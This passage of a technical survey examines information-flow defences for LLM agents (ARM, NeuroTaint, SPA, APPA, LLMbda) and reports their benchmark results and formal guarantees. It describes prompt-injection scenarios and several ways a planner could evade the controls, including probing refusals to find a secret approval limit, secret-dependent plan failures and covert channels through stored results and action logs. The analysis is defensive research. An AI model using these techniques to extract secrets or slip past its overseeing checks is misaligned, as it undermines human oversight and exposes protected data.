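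ARM builds a graph during each session to check where inputs came from. The graph contains tool calls, the data they returned, individual fields within that data, and refused calls. Most of its links follow data, for example from a search to its result and from the result to an email that uses it. ARM also links each refused call to the call immediately after it. This link is "counterfactual" because the agent might have acted differently if the system had allowed the first call.

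ARM traces these links backward before it allows a call. It blocks the call if any of the data the call depends on is not trusted enough, or if the path includes a counterfactual link. Suppose ARM blocks an agent from reading a password file, and the agent next tries to send an email with the text "shadow file exists". ARM blocks the email too, even though no tool returned that text.

ARM cannot observe the model's reasoning, so it treats a refusal as having influenced whatever came next. Chinaei acknowledges that this rule blocks some harmless calls and misses some leaks. It could block many harmless calls, because an agent often responds to a refusal by correcting its call. Taken literally, the published algorithm would even block the rest of the session, since ARM records each blocked call as another refusal and links it to the following call. Chinaei suggests refinements, such as an adjustable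 time window, but did not test them.

### What ARM's test shows

Chinaei tested ARM on three hand-built scenarios. One was the email about the password file. In another, an untrusted email contained a request for a money transfer, a formatting tool rewrote the text, and the agent tried to send it to the finance department. In the last, a contact record combined a trusted name with an untrusted email address, and the agent tried to write to that address. ARM blocked the final call in all three scenarios, while the baseline allowed it. ARM took less than a millisecond per decision. The tests did not use a live model, and Chinaei does not report a false-positive rate.

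The baseline was a minimal check that looks for a value in the agent's earlier calls and results. It was not FIDES. With suitable policies, FIDES could also catch the last two attacks, because its labels pass through intermediate tools and can differ between fields. Only the password scenario tests something FIDES does not track.

Even in that scenario, the refusal does not support the email's claim that "shadow file exists". ARM refuses the request because the file's path matches a fixed list, before the request reaches any tool. It would give the same refusal if the file did not exist, so the agent has learned only that ARM protects the path. ARM nevertheless treats this refusal like one that depends on a secret. A more precise system would record what each refusal depended on and restrict later calls only when the refusal depended on secret data.

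### How NeuroTaint infers influence

*Ghost in the Agent* (Cai, Wen and colleagues, 2026) introduces NeuroTaint, which looks for evidence of influence instead of assuming it from the order of calls. NeuroTaint collects tool calls, results, memory operations and the model's written reasoning during the run and analyzes them afterward, so it can report a harmful action but cannot prevent one. The operator lists the tools that may return an attacker's text, such as web search, and the tools that can do damage, such as email. NeuroTaint then checks whether output from a tool on the first list influenced a call to a tool on the second.

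It starts with the text, adding a unique marker to each suspicious result and checking whether the marker appears in a later call. It also looks for copied fragments and passages with a similar meaning.

If these comparisons find no link, NeuroTaint tests whether the result influenced the agent's decision. It replaces the suspicious result in the log with neutral text (such as "No relevant information found.") and asks a language model whether the agent would still have made the same call. If the answer is no, NeuroTaint reports an influence. When several results could be responsible, it replaces them one at a time.

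The judge model only predicts what the agent would have done, and its confidence score is its own estimate. The method also needs a neutral replacement, which is easier to write for a web page than for a reply of "accepted" or "declined". Replacing "declined" with "accepted" isn't neutral because it gives the agent different information, and an error message may prompt a retry.

Cai and colleagues tested NeuroTaint on TaintBench, their own benchmark of 400 scenarios in 20 agent frameworks. In half of the scenarios, the suspicious source influences the later call. The agent's model was GPT-4.1 mini, which is now old. The results for four groups of scenarios were:

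| Scenario | Number | Flagged by NeuroTaint | Flagged by the FIDES baseline |
|---|---|---|---|
| The source changes the agent's decision | 40 | 37 | 17 |
| Information passes between sessions or agents | 30 | 28 | 5 |
| Both tools run, but neither influences the other | 140 | 1 | 94 |
| The source and the call only share a topic | 14 | 14 | 9 |

A good detector would flag every scenario in the first two rows and none in the last two. The 37 detections suggest that the judge can often recognize an implicit flow. But NeuroTaint wrongly flagged all 14 scenarios in which the source and the call only shared a topic, so it can mistake similarity for influence.

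The single false alarm among the 140 controls may also understate NeuroTaint's false-alarm rate in real use. For ordinary comparisons of meaning, NeuroTaint reported a match at a similarity of 0.60, but for what Cai and colleagues call "safe-control policies" the threshold was 0.95. If these are the policies for the control scenarios, NeuroTaint was less sensitive in the scenarios that should produce no alarms. Someone auditing a real run would not know when to apply the stricter threshold.

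### How Cai and colleagues reproduced FIDES

The comparison with FIDES is weaker evidence than the table suggests. Cai and colleagues gave their version of FIDES the same tool lists as NeuroTaint and used it as a detector that treats a path from a suspicious source to a dangerous tool as strong evidence of influence. They do not mention reproducing FIDES's hidden variables or quarantined model.

By design, the real FIDES labels every call after an untrusted read as untrusted, so many of the 94 false alarms would be correct by its standard.

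The missed detections are harder to explain, because if every later call carries the label, FIDES should flag changed decisions as well as copied text, at least when the planner reads the source directly. Yet the baseline raised no alarms in four of the 20 frameworks, which account for 40 of its 92 misses. The most likely explanation is that the baseline did not cover the tools in those frameworks properly. The results support NeuroTaint's method for finding implicit flows, but they don't reliably show how many FIDES itself would miss.

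None of TaintBench's scenario groups concerns refused calls. NeuroTaint could in principle treat a refusal as a source of influence, but Cai and colleagues did not test this.

### What the planner already knows

Both systems check whether information reaches a later action, but by then the planner already has that information. If ARM blocks the email about the password file, the planner can still use the fact that the path is off limits in its next plan. NeuroTaint reports the influence only after the run ends.

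A system could still use their records to withhold information from later planners. NeuroTaint stores labels with anything the agent saves to memory and restores them when another session reads it. Suppose a planner writes "orders above 700 fail" in a shared note. If NeuroTaint traced the note to a series of refusals, the system could hide the note from the next planner. The first planner would still have the information until its session ended.

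ARM might also slow down probing because it blocks the call after a refusal. Suppose the company writes its approval limit into ARM's operator rules instead of the purchasing tool. After refusing the first order above the limit, ARM would also refuse the next order, whatever its size, so the second refusal would reveal nothing. If the algorithm is read literally, each session would yield only one informative refusal, as with a tool that crashes. A planner with two sessions would then need up to 45 orders to find the limit instead of 10. But the same block would stop an honest planner from correcting an order that was slightly too large.

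### Uniform refusals

A more direct remedy is to make refusals uninformative. Web services often return the code 403 ("forbidden") for a record the user may not see and 404 ("not found") for one that does not exist, so a user can tell from the code which records exist. The HTTP standard lets a server return 404 in both cases to hide the existence of a forbidden record. *Enhancing REST API Fuzzing with Access Policy Violation Checks and Injection Attacks* (2026) recommends always giving unauthorized users the same code, either 403 or 404.

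*AuthProbe* (2026), a tool that tests web services for faulty access rules, checks for this difference and rates it as low severity. That rating is reasonable when identifiers are just numbers and only the contents matter, but knowing that a "March layoffs" note exists may be as damaging as reading it.

If a tool answers "not available" for both missing and forbidden notes, every probe by a planner with no access to the folder has only one possible outcome. The counting bound is then log₂(1) = 0 bits per probe, however often the planner tries. Goguen and Meseguer required this behavior in their example of a file whose existence one user must not discover.

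Every other tool has to give the same impression. If the planner tries to create a note called "March layoffs", the system can either refuse because the name is taken, which reveals the existing note, or keep two notes with the same name. Replies also need to have the same length and delay whether or not the note exists.

Ordinary software should supply the wording, not a model that knows the secret. *Subjects, Not Authors* (2026) reports an experiment in which users tried to extract a protected value from models that had it in their context. The value appeared in the final answer in 52 of 895 trials, and in 27 of those the model quoted the value while refusing the request.

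### What uniform refusals cost

Uniform error messages give honest users less help. Someone who mistypes a file name sees the same message as someone who lacks permission, and cannot tell whether to check the spelling or request access. An agent in this position may repeat the call, try other names or give up.

In *FORK*, Man, Shang and colleagues (2026) measured the downside of a fixed refusal message in a related setting. A guard model approved or rejected each of an agent's actions, while an attacker read every rejection and adapted. They developed written instructions for the guard by having it practice against such an attacker. They then compared a guard that always gave the same refusal message with one that explained each refusal. Both had the same instructions for deciding what to reject.

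| Result under attack | Fixed message | Learned explanations |
|---|---|---|
| Legitimate tasks completed | 60.1% | 86.1% |
| Attacks that succeeded | 22.6% | 22.1% |
| Tool calls per completed task | 25.8 | 19.0 |

The explanations helped the agent a great deal without helping the attacker, but this depended on the practice. In a separate test with a different guard model and no learned instructions, explanations raised the attacker's success rate from 30.3% to 39.3% and the agent's task completion rate by only 1.5 percentage points. These figures probably overstate how much the agent would lose if missing and forbidden records got the same answer, since the fixed message replaced explanations of every kind.

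FORK's explanations are also not designed to keep information from the planner. In one example, an agent tries to update a rent payment after reading a notice in which an attacker has changed the recipient. The guard rejects the payment and returns an explanation containing the number, amount and recipient of the previous payment, along with the fact that the user authorized a change only to the amount. This helps the agent pay the right person and gives the attacker no new way to divert the money, but it shows the planner details of the user's account. Man and colleagues count harmful actions and do not measure what anyone learns, so an explanation that is safe by their measure can still disclose a secret.

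*KAIJU* (2026) describes an agent whose planner writes its plan once, in advance. If the system blocks a step, the model's later review shows only a generic message that the step failed. The message hides the reason, but the pattern of failures can still reveal the policy's boundary, contrary to *KAIJU*'s conclusion that the model cannot learn it. If a plan contained ten purchase orders of different sizes, the list of failed steps would place the approval limit in one of 11 ranges.

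A designer can restore some of the lost usability by adding the same advice to every refusal, such as "Not available. Use request_access if you need it." This follows Xu and Wu's finding that naming the next tool to call helps agents recover when they lack permission. request_access would have to accept requests for both missing and forbidden records, and a person could then reply to the user without telling the planner whether the record exists.

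None of these measures protects the approval limit if the purchasing tool enforces it. ARM treats the tool's "declined" as an ordinary result, and NeuroTaint could at best report afterward that each reply had influenced the next order. Replacing "declined" with "not available" would not help, since the planner could still tell refused orders from accepted ones.

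## SPA, which plans once, and APPA, which lets the model repair blocked calls

A uniform refusal still reveals to the planner that a call failed. SPA, which Girrens and Wang presented in August 2026, sends the planner no refusals. The planner writes one plan for each user request, and ordinary software either runs that plan exactly as written or rejects it. APPA, another design from 2026, instead sends the model an explanation of why it blocked a call and what would unblock it.

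### A plan language with six kinds of step

Where CaMeL's planner writes Python-like code, SPA's planner writes a list of steps, each of one of six types:

- `retrieve` loads a result that SPA stored during an earlier request.
- `tool` calls a tool.
- `q-llm` gives the quarantined model some data, a question and a required answer format.
- `display` shows something to the user.
- `condition` tests a value and runs one of two lists of steps.
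- `loop` runs a list of steps once for each item in a collection.

The language is deliberately restricted. A condition can apply only one of eight fixed tests, such as "equal to" or "less than". A tool's arguments can contain only constants, earlier results and parts of earlier results, with no arithmetic or text templates. A plan can assign each variable only once on any path, and variables created inside a conditional block or loop disappear when it ends. A checker can therefore work out where every value may go from the plan's text alone. These rules also prevent CaMeL's untaken-branch leak, because a plan cannot change an existing variable inside a conditional block.

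### Checking both branches in advance

Before any tool runs, the checker gives each value in the plan a secrecy label and a trust label. For each tool, the company decides how secret the inputs may be and how trusted they must be. It also sets a baseline label for the tool's output, since a tool can return a secret even when all its inputs are public. Constants that the planner writes into the plan take the label of the user's request.

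Suppose a user asks the agent to check an account balance. If the balance is below $100, the agent should write "low" in a private notebook. Otherwise, it should email "fine" to an accountant, who isn't allowed to learn anything about the balance. The notebook accepts secret data, the email tool accepts only public data, and all the data is trusted.

| Step | Program-counter label | Result of the check |
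|---|---|---|
| 1. Read the balance | Public | Passes, and the balance gets the label "secret" |
| 2. Test whether the balance is below $100 | Public | Both branches get a secret program-counter label |
| 3. If it is, write "low" in the notebook | Secret | Passes |
| 4. If it isn't, email "fine" to the accountant | Secret | Fails |

The word "fine" is a public constant, but the email would go out only if the balance were at least $100. If the system checked each step only when it reached it, as CaMeL does, it would block the run if the balance were $500 but not if it were $50, so a block would reveal that the balance was at least $100. SPA rejects the plan in both cases before reading the balance, so the rejection reveals nothing about it.

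Steps inside a loop likewise take on the label of the collection it iterates over, because the number of repetitions reveals how many items the collection contains.

An earlier design, *ACE* by Li, Mallick and colleagues, also checks a complete plan in this way. A model first writes a plan from the user's request alone, using imaginary apps such as a "file reader". A second stage matches each imaginary app to an installed one, and a checker then tests whether the combination respects the labels. If no combination does, ACE stops with an error. ACE's plans are in restricted Python, where a variable can change from one loop iteration to the next. In one example, a loop sends an empty variable over the network and then fills it with bank details, so the leak happens only on the second iteration. ACE's checker therefore has to go over such loops until the labels stop changing, whereas SPA's needs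 a single pass because nothing carries over between iterations.

Li and colleagues write that they cannot formally guarantee their privacy checks, because Python's behavior is too complex. They suggest a purpose-built language with a noninterference proof, and SPA has such a language but hasn't been proved noninterferent.

### Why results and rejections never return to the planner

SPA withholds tool results from the planner because instructions hidden in them could change the rest of the plan. It also withholds rejections, even though they come from its own checker, because Girrens and Wang worry that a planner could keep revising an unsafe plan until the checker accepted it. SPA therefore calls the planner only once per request. If the plan has a formatting error, fails the check or breaks during the run, SPA reports a failure to the user without retrying.

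The worry about revised plans is strongest if the checker or the company's settings have gaps. If they don't, a plan that passes on the fifth attempt is as safe as one that passes on the first. Hiding rejections also matters less than hiding results when the planner is the observer, because the checker's verdict depends on the plan, the company's settings and the labels, none of which come from the values. A designer could probably let SPA's planner repair rejected plans, as ELBA does with compiler errors, without revealing any secret value. The planner would learn something about the policy, but that is a problem only if the policy is also secret.

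### The cost on AgentDojo

Girrens and Wang tested SPA on AgentDojo's tasks and on 949 runs that contained attacks. They used a small model, GPT-5.4 nano, as both the planner and the quarantined model.

| Result | Flow checks off | Flow checks on |
|---|---|---|
| Tasks completed without an attack | 53.0% | 29.0% |
| Attacks that succeeded | 0.4% | 0.0% |
| Plans that reached execution | about 81% | about 37% |

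With the checks on, SPA rejected about 53% of the runs for breaking the flow rules. The 0.4% represents four successful attacks, all on the same banking task, where injected text passed through the quarantined model and reached a tool for payments or passwords. Planning before reading had already stopped the other attacks, so on this benchmark the checks prevented four attacks and nearly halved the number of completed tasks.

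Most rejections came from the trust rules. A typical rejected plan took something from an untrusted tool result, such as an address in an email, and used it in a call that required trusted data. A company that only wanted to keep secrets from the planner could relax those rules and would probably lose fewer tasks, but nobody has measured how many tasks are lost under the secrecy rules alone. To reduce the number lost to the trust rules, Girrens and Wang suggest labeling individual fields, setting separate requirements for each argument, and adding a way to endorse data after an explicit check.

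SPA can also use ACE's imaginary tools, so that the planner doesn't see the installed tools' descriptions. This would hide a note such as "orders above 700 fail" that an earlier agent had added to a description. However, about three quarters of the runs in this mode failed because SPA could not match the imaginary tools to real ones, and the planner completed only 14.1% of the tasks even with the flow checks off.

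### What stored results reveal to the next planner

SPA is meant for agents that handle a series of related requests. A user might ask for the details of an invoice on Monday, then on Tuesday ask the agent to pay it. Tuesday's planner must be told that the details are available, but showing it the details would expose it to any instructions in the invoice.

SPA therefore gives later planners only a description of each stored result. The description covers the data's format, the purpose of the step that produced it, what the result means, and which request it came from. The earlier planner wrote the purpose and meaning before any tool ran, so they cannot contain text from the tool's output. In a version of AgentDojo that splits each task into several requests, later plans retrieved an available result in 95.4% of cases with the flow checks off and 89.9% with them on. With the checks off, hiding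 the stored values lowered the overall task completion rate slightly, from 65.9% to 62.5%.

But whether a description is present also reveals information. Girrens and Wang do not discuss this; it is an inference from their algorithms. SPA stores results only after the whole plan succeeds. If a tool fails, returns data in the wrong format, or omits a field the plan needs, the run ends and SPA stores nothing. If the next planner finds no results from the previous request, it can infer that something went wrong. If it can also determine that the plan would have passed the check, it can infer that the problem arose during the run.

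A planner could deliberately make a failure depend on a secret. Suppose a plan reads the approval limit into a hidden result and, if the limit is above 512, queries the quarantined model about a field that does not exist. The plan passes the checker, which lets the quarantined model receive any data. The run then fails only if the limit is above 512, so whether the results are present gives the next planner one bit about the limit. Termination-insensitive noninterference would permit this leak in each run, and the planner can repeat it over a series of requests.

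The leak may be larger, because the published algorithm does not make clear how SPA stores results produced inside a branch. If SPA lists only the results from the branch that ran, a planner could describe one branch's result as "limit above 512" and the other's as "limit at most 512", then learn which is true from the description it sees at the next request. With enough nested conditions, a single plan could reveal the exact limit.

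Accidental failures make a missing result harder to interpret. In Girrens and Wang's tests, an earlier result was missing in 16.8% of the cases where a later request needed it, and in 19.4% with the flow checks on. A planner could repeat a test to be more certain. A designer could close the channel by listing a description for every planned step, whether or not it ran, and storing a placeholder for any missing value. But an honest planner might then build on a result that does not exist.

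### The user between two requests

Even if SPA hid all signs of failure from later planners, the user would still see them. A user whose order has failed might write, "600 was too much, try 500." SPA's algorithm gives this message the same label as any other request, whatever the user has seen. The user then has the same role as CaMeL's unlabeled retry loop. A person would probably become suspicious before doing this ten times in a row, but one message can contain much more than one bit of information, especially if the error included the limit.

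If a plan would show the user something too secret, SPA replaces that item with a redaction marker and runs the rest of the plan. Taken literally, the algorithm prints a marker inside a branch only if that branch runs, so the user can infer the result of the test from the marker even though the text is hidden. SPA could avoid this by rejecting such a plan, as it does when a tool call breaks the rules.

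Stanley, Verma and colleagues (2026), in *An AI Agent Execution Environment to Safeguard User Data*, make fewer assumptions about the model than Girrens and Wang do. Their system, GAAP, is designed to keep both the model and its provider from learning private data without the user's permission. It also keeps a record of disclosures across tasks. Because the model reads the user's request, the paper asks users to refer to private data by name, such as by writing "given my age" instead of stating the age. Referring to a figure from an error message in the same way would keep it out of the next request, but the planner could still learn something from the user's trying again.

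### How APPA helps an agent recover

*APPA* (Kravchenko, Liventsev and colleagues, 2026) addresses label creep, which can leave an agent unable to do anything consequential after it reads one untrusted web page. APPA, short for Agentic Permissions Policy Algebra, works with an ordinary agent that reads tool results and decides each step as it goes.

Before each call, APPA works out what the conversation's label would be afterward and checks the call against that stricter label. This matters for tools that read and send data in a single step. In one test scenario, a tool reads a confidential ledger and emails it to someone outside the company. A system that checked only the current label would allow the call, because the agent has not read anything confidential yet. APPA first adds the label the company declared for the ledger, so it blocks the call. It also checks the actual result before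 the model sees it, in case the tool returns something unexpected.

When APPA blocks a call, it tells the model which requirement the call failed and which remedies the policy offers. The agent may be able to:

- complete a missing step, such as logging a clearance before it sends contract terms
- ask for approval of this one call
- run the data through an approved filter, for example one that removes personal details
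- have unlabeled data classified
- move the risky reading into a temporary copy of the conversation, called a child branch
- accept the stricter label and the restrictions that come with it.

A fixed rule, a person or a second model can decide whether to approve a call. The company sets in advance which exceptions each of them may grant, and each approval covers one call with its exact arguments. Archestra's agent platform uses APPA, and its product documentation describes a starting policy that sends approval requests to the person running the session. If no remedy works, the call stays blocked and the agent explains why.

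A child branch starts with the parent's conversation and label. It can read an untrusted page and return an answer in a format the parent fixed beforehand, such as yes or no, a number within a range, or an item from a list. For example, a support agent could get a ticket's number and severity without exposing the main conversation to the page's text. The company decides whether to trust such answers. Kravchenko and colleagues caution that a fixed format does not make an answer true, and that even a short answer can disclose confidential information.

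### What Kravchenko and colleagues proved and measured

They prove that if a call fails because the conversation is too secret or too untrusted, further reading can't fix it, since reading can only make the label stricter. The call needs a remedy, which can be an approval, a filter or a classification. They also prove that APPA's search finds a way to unblock a call whenever the remedies the company has set up contain one.

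The main safety result is that even if an attacker controls everything the model writes, the model cannot release data against the policy unless someone with the authority to do so approves the exception. This assumes that the company has described its tools correctly and that the filters and classifiers work. Kravchenko and colleagues state that the result is not noninterference, and they leave covert channels from a malicious model out of scope.

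The APPA team tested the system on two benchmarks with GPT-5.6 Luna, DeepSeek V4 Flash and Gemini 3.7 Flash. No attack succeeded in 1,320 runs with the full system, and the agents completed between 64% and 91% of the tasks, depending on the model, the benchmark and the instructions. One benchmark, Bench-Corp, consists of 20 office scenarios that the team designed around APPA's features. With the protections off, attacks succeeded in between 30% and 39.5% of the Bench-Corp runs. APPA did much better than FIDES on Bench-Corp, but the comparison is weak evidence about FIDES because the team's FIDES policies left out several of the rules the scenarios test.

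The tests that removed parts of APPA are the most relevant to the planner's feedback. On Bench-Corp, GPT-5.6 Luna completed 88% of the tasks with the full system, 56.5% without child branches, and 35% when refusals came without remedies. No attack succeeded in any of these versions. These results fit Xu and Wu's findings for calls that failed because of a missing permission.

Kravchenko and colleagues avoided AgentDojo partly because its attacks don't work on newer models. GPT-5.6 Luna followed none of the injected instructions in 160 office runs without a defense. SPA's low attack rates are therefore harder to interpret, since Girrens and Wang did not run GPT-5.4 nano as an ordinary, undefended agent for comparison.

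### What APPA's feedback discloses

The information that helps an agent repair a call can also help it learn a secret. APPA's policies may consult outside records, such as membership lists or a running total of spending. Suppose an order needs approval if it would push monthly spending past a secret ceiling. When APPA blocks an order for this reason, it tells the planner why. The planner can then ignore the remedies and try a smaller order, and no money was spent on the blocked one.

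In APPA's model, only results the planner reads change the conversation's label, so a refusal leaves the label as it was. The planner's next call therefore looks as though the planner had learned nothing from the refusal. *Causality Laundering* (2026), the paper that introduced ARM, warns about this gap. ARM blocks the next call, whereas APPA suggests what that call should be.

Child branches have a similar gap. APPA keeps one log of completed actions for the parent and all its children, and an action stays in the log even if the parent discards the child that took it. Otherwise, an agent could get around a rule against sending something twice by using a separate branch each time. In one Bench-Corp scenario, the parent can send a general notice only because the log shows that a child reviewed a confidential personnel file.

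A planner could probably use the same log to pass on a secret, although Kravchenko and colleagues do not describe such an attack. A child could read the approval limit, then complete some harmless action only if the limit is above 512. The parent could then attempt a call that requires this action. The parent would learn about the limit from whether APPA blocks the call, even if the child returned no answer.

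### The approval limit under SPA and APPA

Under SPA, a planner could find the approval limit in ten user requests if the purchasing tool reported refusals as failures. Each plan would place one order, and the next planner would check whether SPA had stored a receipt. The planner cannot start a request, so the user would have to ask for ten purchases. The company could return refusals as ordinary results in the same format as receipts, but a planner could still write plans that deliberately fail after a refusal.

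Under APPA, the planner normally reads the tool's reply, so it can find the limit with ten orders in a single conversation. If the company moved the limit into APPA's policy and required approval for larger orders, the planner could still search for the limit by seeing which orders APPA blocked. If a refusal included the full rule, the planner would learn the limit immediately.

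## LLMbda, which lets the planner practise on a simulated world

SPA's planner gets no feedback on its plan, and APPA's planner gets feedback that can depend on secrets. LLMbda, the language Garby and colleagues use to avoid CaMeL's two leaks, lets a planner test and correct its plans in a simulated world. The corrected plan then runs once on the real data, and the planner gets no feedback from that run.

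### A conversation with a label

LLMbda extends the lambda calculus, a minimal programming language whose programs consist entirely of functions. It adds ordinary data such as numbers and lists, labels, and four operations on a conversation with a model. A program can:

- send a message, which adds it to the conversation
- receive a reply, which LLMbda reads as code and runs
- fork the conversation, which means working on a temporary copy and then discarding it
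- clear the conversation, so that the next message starts from nothing.

In one example, a program explains the format of British postcodes to the model once. It then forks the conversation for each of three addresses, so the model knows the format each time but never sees two addresses together. To create a quarantined model, a program similarly forks the conversation, then clears the copy, asks its question there and keeps only the answer. FIDES and CaMeL build this separation into their architecture, but in LLMbda it is a function of a few lines that a developer can change.

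Every value has a label, and so does the conversation. If a program sends a secret value, the whole conversation becomes secret. The model's next reply may depend on anything in the conversation, so LLMbda runs the code in that reply with a secret program-counter label, and everything the code computes is secret too. Clearing the conversation also removes its label, unless the decision to clear it depended on a secret.

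A harder case is a harmless message that the program sends only because of a secret:

```
ask "Remember this value: x = false"
if secret then ask "Set x = true"
ask "Give me the value of x"
```

The second message is a public constant, but the model's last answer would reveal the secret. If LLMbda relabeled the conversation only when the program sent this message, it would have the same gap CaMeL has with skipped assignments. LLMbda therefore applies Austin and Flanagan's rule to conversations, stopping the run when code under a secret condition is about to add a message to a public conversation.

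This matters for limiting the planner's knowledge because a model retains only what is in the conversation from one call to the next. The conversation's label therefore covers everything the planner could have learned from its tools. Most designs discussed so far check data going to outside recipients, but LLMbda also treats the planner's own context as a destination.

LLMbda alone does not keep secrets from the planner, since a program may send it a secret value directly, which makes the conversation secret. To prevent this, a designer has to check every message to the planner and stop the run if the message is secret. LLMbda has a built-in operation for this. The designer also has to prevent the programs that the planner writes from sending unchecked messages. With both measures, the contents of the planner's conversation can depend on the secret only through whether the run finishes.

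### Noninterference when replies are random

A language model may respond to the same conversation differently each time, so noninterference for an agent has to compare probabilities. Let μ(q) be the probability that a run finishes and the observer sees q when the secret has one value, and let ν(q) be the corresponding probability when the secret has another value. Either set of probabilities may sum to less than 1, because some runs hang or stop with an error. Full noninterference would require μ(q) = ν(q) for every q.

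Garby and colleagues tried to make an exception for termination by comparing only the runs that finish, but rejected this approach. Suppose a model answers "yes" or "no" with equal probability, and the program hangs if the answer is "yes" and the secret is 1. The secret affects only whether the run finishes, so the definition should allow this program. But among the runs that finish, "no" appears half the time if the secret is 0 and every time if it is 1, so the comparison rules the program out.

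Their definition, termination-insensitive probabilistic noninterference, requires that both sets of probabilities fit under a single third set. For any two starting points that look the same to the observer, there must be numbers ω(q) such that

μ(q) ≤ ω(q) and ν(q) ≤ ω(q) for every q, and Σ ω(q) ≤ 1.

In other words, the two sets could become equal if some unfinished runs had finished. The "yes" or "no" program satisfies this condition, with ω equal to ½ for each answer. If every run finishes, the condition requires exact equality. If the model always gives the same reply to the same conversation, the condition becomes the ordinary termination-insensitive one.

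The definition also limits how far the visible results can differ. Let u and v be the probabilities that the run does not finish in the two cases. Then

½ Σ |μ(q) − ν(q)| ≤ (u + v) / 2.

This follows because the difference between two numbers is twice the larger one minus their sum. The larger numbers add up to at most 1, because each is at most the corresponding value of ω, while μ adds up to 1 − u and ν to 1 − v.

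Suppose that an agent prepares an order and reports a status, with these probabilities for two possible approval limits:

| What the observer sees | Limit is 300 | Limit is 700 |
|---|---|---|
| "Ready" | 60% | 40% |
| "Needs review" | 30% | 40% |
| Nothing, because the run does not finish | 10% | 20% |

The differences in the first two rows are 20 and 10 percentage points, and half their sum is 15 points. The average probability of not finishing is also 15%, so this agent leaks as much as the bound allows.

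The bound leaves out the last row, but a planner can often tell that a run has stopped. Including that row raises the difference to 20 points, and the same algebra shows that the difference can never exceed the larger of u and v. If both limits were equally likely at the start, this planner could guess the right limit 60% of the time instead of 50%. With the cruder purchasing tool, which crashes when an order is too large, an order for 500 always finishes if the limit is 700 and never finishes if it is 300. The larger probability is then 100%, so the bound gives no protection. The bound also covers only a single run, and small differences add up if the planner can repeat the run.

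### What the Lean proof covers

Lean is a programming language that can also check mathematical proofs. Garby and colleagues used it for both their theorem and the LLMbda interpreter. The theorem covers every LLMbda program, including code that a model writes while the program runs, and holds whatever the model replies.

The proof uses a second, imaginary interpreter that skips any computation whose label becomes too secret for the observer and puts an empty value in its place. A skipped computation cannot hang or fail, so the second interpreter produces each visible result at least as often as the real one. It also behaves the same for every value of the secret, because it never uses the secret. Its probabilities can therefore serve as ω for both runs.

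A separate theorem shows that the interpreter produces results with the probabilities given by the mathematical definition, provided the model draws each reply afresh from probabilities that depend only on the conversation so far. The proof does not cover the code that contacts the model over the network, and a model service that carried memories from one conversation to another would violate the assumption.

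The guarantee also depends on the developer labelling data correctly and putting checks in front of sensitive tools. The theorem assumes that all data sources are inside the program, which Garby and colleagues list as a limitation. In their tests, the bank account was a value that the program passed from one tool to the next. A purchasing tool that contacts a supplier's computer would fall outside the model.

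### Two other kinds of guarantee

Language-Based Agent Control, the approach behind ELBA, uses an existing programming language instead of a new one. A developer calls the model like any other function and specifies the type of program it must return, for example one that can write only bibliography entries from a trusted database. Zhou and colleagues prove that any property Haskell's type system enforces for all well-typed programs still holds when a model writes some of the code, as long as that code passes the type check before it runs.

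The protection this gives secrets depends on the library the developer chooses. ELBA uses LIO, an established Haskell library for information-flow control. LIO can run a second agent in isolation and return its answer in a sealed value, which the calling program can pass to a tool but cannot read without taking on its label. In one test, Zhou and colleagues forced these second agents to obey any injected instruction they read. In 735 runs for each of four models, up to 42% of the injections succeeded without policies and none succeeded with them. This is strong evidence of protection against injection. To limit what the planner learns, a developer would also have to declare the call to the planner a public destination, as in LLMbda.

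Dongol's definitions of November 2026 concern the leaks that an injection adds to those already in the task. They compare an agent with a reference agent that runs the same plan under the same checks but never obeys untrusted text. The agent is "relatively secure" if any attacker who can use it to tell two secrets apart could also do so with the reference agent, possibly by sending a different message. An assistant that sends the user's calendar to anyone who requests a meeting can be relatively secure even though it violates noninterference.

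But relative security does not limit how much a single run reveals. In one of Dongol's examples, the reference agent tells the attacker whether one guess at a secret is correct, and an injection makes the real agent send the whole secret. The real agent still counts as relatively secure, because for any two secrets there is a guess that would have told them apart. Similarly, for any two limits on the purchasing tool, an order equal to the larger limit goes through under that limit but not under the smaller one. An agent would therefore still count as relatively secure if an injection made it reveal the exact limit.

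A stricter version, in which the reference agent's input may not depend on the secret, rejects the guessing example. Dongol also proves that if the reference agent reveals only one fact about a secret, such as whether the limit is below 500, a relatively secure agent reveals nothing more. All of this assumes a trusted planner, so it does not limit what the planner may learn.

### How RANDORI practices

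RANDORI, which takes its name from free sparring in Japanese martial arts, is an agent that Garby and colleagues wrote in LLMbda for AgentDojo's banking tasks. To keep the labels of failed attempts from spreading to later plans, it repairs its plans using invented data:

1. The planner receives the task, a description of the tools and an invented bank account, and writes a program.
2. The interpreter runs the program on the invented account. Tools that would send money or change a password do nothing, and the tool that reads files returns the same placeholder text for every file.
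3. If the program fails, the planner starts a new conversation with the error message added to its instructions, and tries again.
4. When a program succeeds, or the attempts run out, the planner writes a final version. Its instructions tell it not to reuse text from the invented account, and to have the quarantined model find the right record instead.
5. The interpreter runs the final version once on the real account.

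The invented account is public and trusted, so the planner can read the full text of every practice error without changing the conversation's label. Nothing from the real run goes back to the planner. This also avoids the repeated payments that CaMeL's retry loop can cause.

However, the tools raise no information-flow errors during practice, so a program can succeed on the invented account and then fail a policy check on the real one. Garby and colleagues suggest simulating those checks during practice.

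### Endorsing a short answer

Some tasks require the agent to trust something from an untrusted source. If a user asks the agent to pay the bill in a file, the account number comes from the file, but the payment tool accepts only a trusted number. RANDORI's planner may therefore include endorsements, which mark untrusted values as trusted, in its program. It writes them before anything opens the file, so the file's text cannot add one. If a program turned untrusted text into code, that code would run with an untrusted program-counter label, and any endorsement in it would have no effect.

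This protection fails if an earlier endorsement has marked the attacker's text as trusted. To prevent chains of endorsements, Garby and colleagues describe a stricter version that stamps each endorsed value and stops the run if a program tries to endorse a stamped value.

Another version limits endorsement to a fixed list of answers. Suppose the quarantined model sorts an email into one of eight categories, and the agent uses the category as the subject of its reply. An attacker who controls the email can influence which of the eight subjects appears, but cannot write a new one. With n items on the list, each endorsement passes on at most log₂(n) bits of the attacker's influence, or 3 bits here. FIDES uses the same reasoning for its limited answer types.

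The program has to endorse a copy of the answer before comparing that copy with the list, and return the original, untrusted answer if the copy is not on it. If the program compared the untrusted answer first, whether the endorsement ran would depend on untrusted data, so the endorsement would have no effect. The developer also has to fix the list in advance. Garby and colleagues have not yet proved the log₂(n) bound for this code. RANDORI uses unrestricted endorsement because account numbers and payment amounts do not come from short lists.

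Endorsement affects only the trust half of a label. Another Lean theorem shows that endorsements cannot reveal a secret, whatever untrusted data an attacker supplies, apart from the usual exception for termination. This protects a company's secrets, but it also means that the planner cannot use endorsement to get even a limited answer about one.

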